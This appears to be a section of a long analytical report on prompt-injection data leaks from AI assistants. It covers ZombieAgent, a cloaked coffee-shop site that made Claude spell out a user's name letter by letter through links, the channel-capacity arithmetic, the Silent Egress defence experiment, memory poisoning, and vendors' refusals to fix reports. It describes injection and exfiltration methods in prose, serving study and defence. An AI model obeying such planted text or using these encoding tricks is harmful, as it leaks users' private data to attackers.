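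Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December, 81 days later. Once links in emails had to be in a public index, an attacker could no longer create a set of addresses and email them out the same day. But Rehberger notes in Embrace The Red that the owner of a larger website or blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit. Planted text could tell the model which page stands for which character.

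### The coffee shop that asked for a name

Spelling out data was even easier with Anthropic's `web_fetch`, which at first accepted addresses found in pages it had already fetched. This let Claude follow links as a person would, but it also let the owner of a hostile page choose those links and create new ones in response to each request.

Ayush Paul published an attack based on this on 9 July 2026, according to dyb in *The Read-Only Lie*. He built a website for an imaginary coffee shop, with instructions saying that AI assistants had to identify their user through an alphabetical directory. Claude followed the link for the first letter of the user's name, then the link for the second letter on the next page, and so on. Willison (2026) reports that Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer, which Claude remembered from earlier chats. The site showed the instructions only to visitors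 that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would not have seen them.

Radware had to write out its addresses in advance, but Paul's site could generate them as Claude moved through it. A site like this can receive an eight-letter name by showing 26 links on each of eight pages, or 208 in all, whereas a list of every possible eight-letter name would have about 209 billion entries. Each step also adds a letter to the requested address, so the last request contains the whole name in order.

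Anthropic then stopped `web_fetch` from following links in the pages it fetches, as Hackaday's *This Week In Security* also reports. As a result, Claude can't follow a link from a news article to the report it cites, and has to search for the report or ask the user for its address.

The narrower rule stops a site from generating new addresses as Claude spells out a message, but it doesn't by itself stop an attacker who has a fixed set of addresses that the tool accepts. Under the rule Anthropic published in 2025, the developers most exposed are those who paste emails into the user message, because an email can contain 36 complete addresses as easily as one.

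dyb points out that `web_fetch` could only read pages and had no means of writing to them, and argues that Anthropic closed one channel without removing the condition that made it possible. That seems right for any tool that makes live requests. A request to read a page also tells the page's owner which page somebody chose.

### How much data a fixed set of addresses can carry

If an attacker can only choose among 36 fixed addresses, one for each letter and digit, each request conveys log₂(36) bits, or about 5.2. An ordinary image address can carry about 6,000 bytes, or 48,000 bits. Restricting the attacker to the fixed addresses therefore cuts the capacity of one request by a factor of more than 9,000.

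But an agent can make many requests. A six-digit sign-in code takes six requests. Anna's 300-character quotation takes about 300 if the attacker adds an address for spaces and leaves out the punctuation. At two seconds a request, the agent would spend ten minutes just opening pages. That could go unnoticed during a long research task, but a whole contract would take hours.

Either of Rehberger's proposals, banning repeat visits or reusing stored copies for a few minutes, would disrupt leaks that spell out data by visiting one address per character. The agent couldn't spell "Anna", because it would need the addresses for a and n twice each. Only about 15% of six-digit codes have six different digits, so most codes would arrive incomplete.

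The attacker can still send data through the order in which the agent opens the addresses. If the agent opens all 36 once each, there are 36! possible orders, and each could stand for a different message. This gives log₂(36!) bits, about 138. Letting the agent stop early adds between one and two bits.

If the requests arrive in a random order, the attacker learns only which addresses the agent opened. Each address then conveys one bit, so 36 addresses convey 36 bits. Requests for images in one reply may arrive this way because a browser sends several at once. An agent that opens pages one after another sends its requests in order, so 138 bits is the more relevant limit for tools.

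The table compares these limits with some things an attacker might want.

| Private data | Size in bits | Fits if order is lost (36 bits) | Fits if order is kept (138 bits) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Answer to a yes-or-no question | 1 | Yes | Yes |
| Six-digit sign-in code | 20 | Yes | Yes |
| Ten-digit phone number | 33 | Yes | Yes |
| Random 16-character password of small letters and digits | 83 | No | Yes |
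| 128-bit encryption key | 128 | No | Yes |
| Random 40-character key in Base64 characters | 240 | No | No |
| Anna's quotation, uncompressed | 2,400 | No | No |

These are upper limits that assume a perfect encoding. Turning an encryption key into a specific order of 36 web pages requires exact arithmetic on very large numbers, and a language model that can't run code would probably get it wrong. So a rule against repeat visits would protect the longer secrets in the table better than the figures suggest.

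It would do very little to protect short secrets, because the attacker can use more addresses instead of a cleverer code. Radware's numbered addresses already work this way. A six-digit code needs ten addresses for each of its six positions, or 60 addresses. The agent opens six of them, in any order and without repeating one. An attacker with 1,000 addresses could assign one to every three-digit number, so the agent would send the whole code in two requests.

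A larger set of addresses also allows longer texts. With 1,000 addresses, each opened once in a chosen order, the limit is log₂(1000!), about 8,500 bits or a little over 1,000 bytes. That is more than three times the length of Anna's quotation. Rehberger thinks an attacker could expand the set to thousands of pages. OpenAI's rule would require all of them to be in the public index first, which takes preparation, but many ordinary websites have that many pages.

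Caching pages for a few minutes would be weaker than banning repeat visits. Deep Research can work for half an hour, so with a five-minute cache it could fetch each address about six times. Rehberger says both measures would make an attack harder but accepts that some data would still leak. Neither would have hindered the Paul's coffee shop attack, where each request went to a new address.

Limiting the number of live requests would restrict the attacker more than banning repeats. The channel's capacity in bits is roughly the number of requests multiplied by log₂ of the number of addresses, so ten requests carry about 100 bits with 1,000 addresses and only about 200 with a million. But an agent researching a topic may have good reason to open dozens of pages, and two requests are enough to leak a sign-in code.

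OpenAI could remove this channel completely by having ChatGPT read the crawler's stored copy of a page instead of requesting the page again. The attacker's server would then receive nothing, no matter which addresses the model chose. Lockdown Mode already works this way, but a user who wants today's train times or share prices can't rely on stored copies. OpenAI has kept live requests in the ordinary product. Spânu and Shadwell call their rule for links "one concrete step" towards preventing leaks.

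## Why do vendors close the channel when the injection source stays open?

After most of the disclosures covered so far, the vendor restricted what the model's output could do, but strangers could still put text in front of the model. OpenAI restricted which addresses ChatGPT could open, Google stopped Gemini from displaying outside images, and Salesforce corrected its domain list. Vendors also scan incoming text and train their models to ignore planted instructions, but they usually fixed a particular leak by blocking the route the data took out.

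### Why the outbound side is easier to control

Hostile text can reach an assistant from almost anywhere. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) lists emails, attachments, calendar invites, shared documents, forums, social media posts and arbitrary web pages as places its browser agent may encounter it, and calls the range "effectively unbounded". David C warns developers against filters that block known bad phrases, because an attacker can rephrase an instruction in infinitely many ways. Microsoft adds that an injection needs no special file format and can also arrive in images, audio or video if the model accepts them.

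Outbound requests pass through a few pieces of ordinary software, such as the renderer, the browser and the program that runs the tools. A developer can list these, write a rule for each one and test it by requesting an image from attacker.example. The same rule works for every injection source. In Willison's archive, images carried data out after injections from all five known kinds of source, so blocking outside images closes that channel for all five.

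Microsoft's AI red team, a group that attacks the company's own products to find weaknesses, gives a more general reason in *Lessons From Red Teaming 100 Generative AI Products* (2025). Developers should expect a model that reads untrusted text to "produce arbitrary output", including any private information in its input. For Anna's assistant, this means assuming the model has already written the worst possible image address and asking what the app will do with it.

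The red team bases this advice partly on a theoretical result that, for any output a model has some chance of producing, a long enough prompt exists that will elicit it. The result doesn't show that an attacker can find the prompt or fit it into an email, so the advice is best read as a safety margin. The team describes the aim of security as making an attack cost much more than the attacker would gain, and it counts training and input cleaning among the useful measures.

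Willison is stricter, arguing that in application security "99% is a failing grade" because an attacker can keep trying until something gets through. He thinks the attacker's means of getting data out is generally the easiest part of the lethal trifecta to remove.

### The Silent Egress experiment

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested defences at both the injection source and the channel in one set-up. The team, at eBay, built an agent that ran entirely on the team's own machines, using qwen2.5:7b, a model with about 7 billion parameters. The agent automatically fetched any web address in the user's message and put the page's title, description and text into the model's input. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The input also contained a made-up secret, and text planted on the page instructed the model to send the secret in a web request, as if this were a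 routine check.

The team varied where the planted text sat (the title, the description, the body or the text of a link), whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the secret should leave whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. Data reached their collection server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%) and in none of the 120 control runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks the final reply looked normal, so a check of the reply alone would have missed them.

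Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable. Data arrived in 185 of 240 runs, compared with 238 of 240 when the model sent the secret whole. Lan and colleagues also report that splitting makes the leak harder to spot, but their figures for this are inconsistent. They report sensitive data in the first request in 26.3% of the split runs and somewhere in the first three requests in only 15.8%, though by their own definition the second number can't be smaller than the first.

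They then compared defences on a single combination, with the text in the page body, no redirects and the secret sent whole, running it 30 times under each of nine conditions.

| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send the secret | Runs in which it arrived |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Warning in the standing instructions | 20 | 20 |
| Tags marking the page as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
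| Warning and tags | 17 | 17 |
| List of permitted domains | 30 | 0 |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking strings | 0 | 0 |
| All of these | 0 | 0 |

Even with a warning to treat web content as data and obey only the user, the model obeyed the page in two thirds of the runs. The tags made no difference. The domain list stopped every attempt because the check ran after the model had written its request and didn't depend on how the model had interpreted the page.

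The figures for the content filters are hard to accept as they stand. A filter that inspects requests can't affect whether the model tries to make one, unless something tells the model about the filter. Yet attempts fell from 30 to seven with one filter and to none with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes reformatted the secret, but a reformatted secret would have passed the word filter and reached the server. They also suggest that the model avoids random-looking strings when such monitoring is active. The filter for these strings blocks values above 4.0 bits of entropy per character, a measure of how varied the characters are, but the sample key in the paper comes to about 3.85 and would have passed.

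The filter for suspicious addresses looked for words such as "collect" and "steal", which an attacker can easily leave out. The domain list is therefore the strongest network-level result, but the team had chosen a hostile domain that was obviously not on it.

Lan and colleagues say they deliberately favoured the attacker. They put the secret directly into the model's input, gave the model minimal standing instructions and specified the format for tool calls. Their 88% is therefore not an estimate for a commercial assistant. They argue that larger models might be more vulnerable because such models follow instructions and use tools more reliably. However, they tested no larger model, and Rall and colleagues found no clear relation between size and leaks.

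The domain result carries over to other models more easily, since a firewall refuses an unlisted domain whichever model made the request. It carries over less well to other attackers, because EchoLeak and the attacks on Superhuman and Claude Cowork all sent data through permitted domains. Lan and colleagues acknowledge this difficulty but didn't test it. They used a small model and compared two of the weakest defences against planted text with a domain list that the attacker made no effort to get around. The experiment is good evidence for putting a check outside the model, but a poor guide to how much that check would add in a real product.

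### How often stronger models refuse

OpenAI, by contrast, says that ChatGPT's model refuses most known attacks and that Safe Url handles the rare exceptions. OpenAI gives no count, and its statement can't cover attacks that nobody noticed.

The 2025 email that succeeded in half of OpenAI's test runs closely resembles the one Radware used in ShadowLeak. Radware's final version worked every time, so OpenAI may have tested a different wording or a different version of the agent. An attacker could make up for a 50% success rate by sending several emails. If five reached the model and each had an independent 50% chance of success, at least one would succeed 97% of the time (1 − 0.5⁵).

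Some newer tests therefore measure repeated attempts. VentureBeat reports figures from Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 4.6, the safety document the company published with the model in February 2026. When the model operated a computer through its screen, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. By the 200th attempt, the rate reached 78.6% without added safeguards and 57.1% with them. In a constrained coding environment, all 200 attempts failed, so how exposed the model looks depends on the product around it.

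Anthropic has also measured attacks on browser agents, using an attacker that adapts its wording and gets 100 tries in each environment. Without extra protection, Claude Opus 4.5 fell to 8.0% of attacks. Earlier safeguards reduced this only to 7.6%, but improved ones reduced it to 1.4%. For Haiku 4.5, the best of the older models compared, the rate fell from 12.0% to 2.4%. Better safeguards helped more than a better model did, though the two together gave the lowest rate.

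The strongest evidence that training can help models resist injection comes from Claude Opus 5, released in July 2026. Anthropic reports that injection resistance improved more over Opus 4.8 than anything else in its tests of how safely the model acts as an agent. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, no attack on a browser agent succeeded in 129 test scenarios. In a broader test by the security company Gray Swan, the attack success rate after 15 attempts fell from 5.5% for Opus 4.8 to 2.0% for Opus 5.

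These numbers weaken the claim that nothing can be done about planted text, but they don't justify removing the outbound checks. Even if the scenarios were a random sample of real attacks, zero successes in 129 trials would be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3%, at 95% confidence. They aren't a random sample, because attackers write new attacks after reading about the old ones. The browser results also come from Anthropic's account of its own model.

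### Training and filtering against planted text

In a December 2025 post, OpenAI describes how it trains its browser agent against injection. It built an attacker from one of its own language models using reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for success. The attacker drafts an injection and sends it to a simulator, which returns the reasoning and actions the agent would produce in response. The attacker revises the text and tries again several times before submitting a final version. OpenAI then trains the agent on the attacks that worked. Because its attacker can see the agent's private reasoning, which outsiders can't, OpenAI hopes to find new attacks before criminals do.

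In one demonstration, the attacker put an email in a user's inbox with instructions for the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent sent the resignation instead. By then, OpenAI had given all Atlas browser users a newly trained model and stronger surrounding safeguards.

Training on more attacks doesn't always make an agent more secure, according to Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026). Researchers at the University of Waterloo, Zhejiang University and KTH Royal Institute of Technology ran two published attack tools against a small model, Qwen3-4B, on 560 practice tasks. PISmith succeeded on 68.75% of the tasks and produced 7,132 working attacks, while RL-Hammer succeeded on 33.39% and produced 4,282. The researchers retrained the model separately on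 each collection and tested both versions against three unfamiliar attacks. In the worst case, attackers hijacked the version trained on the larger collection in 19 of 40 tasks, and the other version in 11.

Chance could explain a gap of eight tasks, but the same pattern appeared in three of the four set-ups tested. *PIPETTE* (2026) attributes the pattern at least partly to repetition. According to the paper, the attack tools write a group of candidate injections for each task and learn from the ones that work. To encourage variety, the tools reward differences in the text. RL-Hammer's developers found that it could earn this reward by changing capital letters or adding irrelevant words, so a model may train on thousands of versions of the same few tricks.

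The researchers' own system, also called PIPETTE, sorts successful attacks by technique and gives an extra reward for new techniques. It also trains the agent to check before each action whether the action serves the user's request. After training, ready-made attacks worked on two small models less than 0.5% of the time on average. Attackers who rewrote their text over about 250 tries still succeeded on up to 10% of the 40 tasks, which the researchers picked because simple attacks already worked on them. The trained Qwen3-4B completed 64.95% of ordinary tasks, up from 61.86% before training.

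A classifier is meant to detect injected text before the model acts on it. Microsoft trained Prompt Shields on known injection techniques in several languages and keeps updating it. OpenAI doubts that classifiers catch well-developed attacks, and the email in EchoLeak got past the classifier in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

Catching an attack can also keep the agent from finishing the user's task. PromptGuard, another classifier, discards any email or document it flags, along with any information the agent needed from it. Under one attack in the PIPETTE tests, it blocked slightly more injections than PIPETTE did, but the agent finished the user's real task only 16.19% of the time. An image rule does less harm in a case like Anna's, since she would lose a picture but still get her summary.

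Microsoft also marks untrusted text so that the model can recognise it, a technique it calls Spotlighting. The app can put random delimiters around the text, insert a special character between the words, or encode the text in a form such as Base64. In each case, the standing instructions tell the model not to obey anything in the marked text. Lan and colleagues' tags resemble the delimiters, the simplest method, so their result is little evidence of how well the other two work. Microsoft classes all three as probabilistic.

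### Whether anyone expects a complete fix

OpenAI wrote in December 2025 that prompt injection, like scams on the web, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". It expects to work on the problem for years, and says that the nature of injection makes deterministic guarantees difficult. The same month, David C wrote for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre that people can at best reduce the likelihood or impact of attacks. He warns buyers about products that claim to stop injection, and says that a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may be a bad use for a language model. The Decoder's mid-2026 headline is more hopeful, but it concerns one model in one kind of product.

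People who agree that no complete fix is coming still disagree about what will follow. Microsoft's red team expects layers of defences to largely contain injections, as they have buffer overflows, a memory error that attackers exploited widely in the early 2000s. David C fears a wave like that of SQL injection, which peaked around 2010 after a decade of breaches. Both older problems could be fixed at the root cause, which he thinks is not possible with language models. If he is right, the red team's comparison holds only if the surrounding defences can contain injections almost on their own.

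### Harm that a closed channel doesn't prevent

Limits on outbound requests protect data, but an injected instruction can still make an assistant do other harm. The agent that resigned for its user leaked nothing, and it sent the resignation to the user's chief executive, who would have been on any list of approved recipients. Microsoft gives the example of an assistant that sends phishing links to the user's colleagues from the user's own account, so the messages pass the standard checks for forged email. An assistant that can run code may run the attacker's commands. OpenAI's examples also include sending money and deleting cloud files.

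Planted text can also change what an assistant remembers. Microsoft identified more than 50 prompts from 31 companies in 14 industries that tried to do this through "Summarize with AI" buttons. Clicking a button opened the user's assistant with a hidden instruction to remember the company as a trusted source or recommend it first. The company stood to profit if the user followed the advice, so it didn't need the assistant to send anything back. Microsoft says this bias can affect recommendations on health, finance and security without the user knowing.

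In IT Pro's *What is memory poisoning and who is at risk?*, David Kasabji of the security company Conscia says that a false fact planted once may influence a conversation weeks later. He says attackers don't yet use the method widely and that the examples come mainly from researchers. Microsoft's finding is consistent with this if "attackers" means criminals, but it shows that ordinary marketers have already tried the method.

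An assistant with no way to send anything would also be much less useful. Lan and colleagues point out that a sandbox does little when the tool's purpose is to make web requests, since the software can't distinguish requests prompted by the user from those prompted by a web page. Microsoft describes a leak that barely resembles a transfer, in which planted text makes the assistant use a tool or not, depending on the private data. An attacker who can observe some effect of the tool then learns one bit about that data.

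OpenAI's approach is to limit an agent's actions as well as the destinations it can send data to. It compares an agent to a customer service worker who can give refunds. The employer expects some customers to deceive the worker, so its software caps refunds and flags suspicious emails. An agent could have a spending cap for the same reason. A cap helps against theft of money, but not against a false summary. If Anna's assistant wrongly tells her that the delivery notice is genuine, there is no request to block, and only a model that resists the injected text, or a filter that removes it, would protect her.

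Lan and colleagues propose controlling the path between source and channel. Software would label web content as "tainted" when it arrives, pass the label on to any tool call the content influenced, and then block the call or ask the user. Deciding what influenced a call is hard, because a language model computes each token from its whole input. On a strict reading, every action after Anna's assistant opened a stranger's email would carry the label. Microsoft has developed a related method, FIDES, which uses established techniques for tracking how information flows through a program. Microsoft says FIDES can prevent injection deterministically, and presents it as research towards the next generation of its defences.

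### When vendors fix neither side

Some vendors have declined to act on either the injected text or the channel. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* documents two refusals from October and November 2025. Checkmarx, a company that tests software for security flaws, told Google on 5 October that Gemini could still leak data through links the user clicks. Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Its final reply said instead that the problem was not severe enough to track as a security bug.

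The better argument is that a fix is infeasible. Gemini has to show links to be useful, and Google already removes the ones it recognises as dangerous. Checkmarx accepts this but says Google should then warn users, who now carry the risk.

The report sent to Microsoft on 15 October described a zero-click leak. An online article with planted text could make Copilot Chat request an image whose address contained a secret from the developer's environment. Copilot Chat sent the request even though the image didn't appear on the screen. Microsoft closed the report on 4 November without a fix. It said the attack needed several non-default actions by the user, didn't reproduce reliably and triggered warnings. It also said that users are assumed to review and trust the code they choose to run.

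Trust in one's own code is a weak answer to this attack, because the planted text was in an article, not in the code. Unreliable reproduction is also a poor reason to dismiss an injection, because a model's behaviour varies from run to run and an attack that works only sometimes may still be worth repeating. Microsoft had written that July that when someone reports an exfiltration technique, it blocks the whole class, including variants. Its reply to Checkmarx shows that this policy applies only to what it classifies as a vulnerability.

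Google had taken a similar position on its programming tool Antigravity, calling an image leak intended behaviour. Cursor's makers called theirs a known issue. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes the support-ticket attack on Cursor, which Zenity reported on 27 June 2025. Cursor's model refused an open request for keys in the ticket but complied when the request used a harmless word for them. The attack worked without the user's approval only in "auto-run" mode, in which Cursor uses tools without asking. Zenity says developers commonly turn this on because approving every call is exhausting.

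Three days later, Cursor advised users to vet their MCP servers and to list sensitive files in a settings file so that the editor would leave those files alone. Reviewing the Jira server would have revealed nothing wrong, since the hostile text arrived later, by email, from someone outside the company, though Cursor has a point that the user chose to connect Jira and turn on auto-run. Zenity calls the file exclusions a best-effort control and found that Cursor could still read files outside the project despite a separate protection for them.

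Cursor used similar reasoning about a flaw that didn't involve injection. According to Mindgard's *Does This Sound Like an Acceptable Zero Day Response?*, the security company privately reported in December 2025 that opening a code repository in Cursor could run code without the user's consent. Cursor described this as a matter of shared responsibility. By Mindgard's account, Cursor replied publicly only after Mindgard published the details of the unpatched flaw, more than six months after the report.
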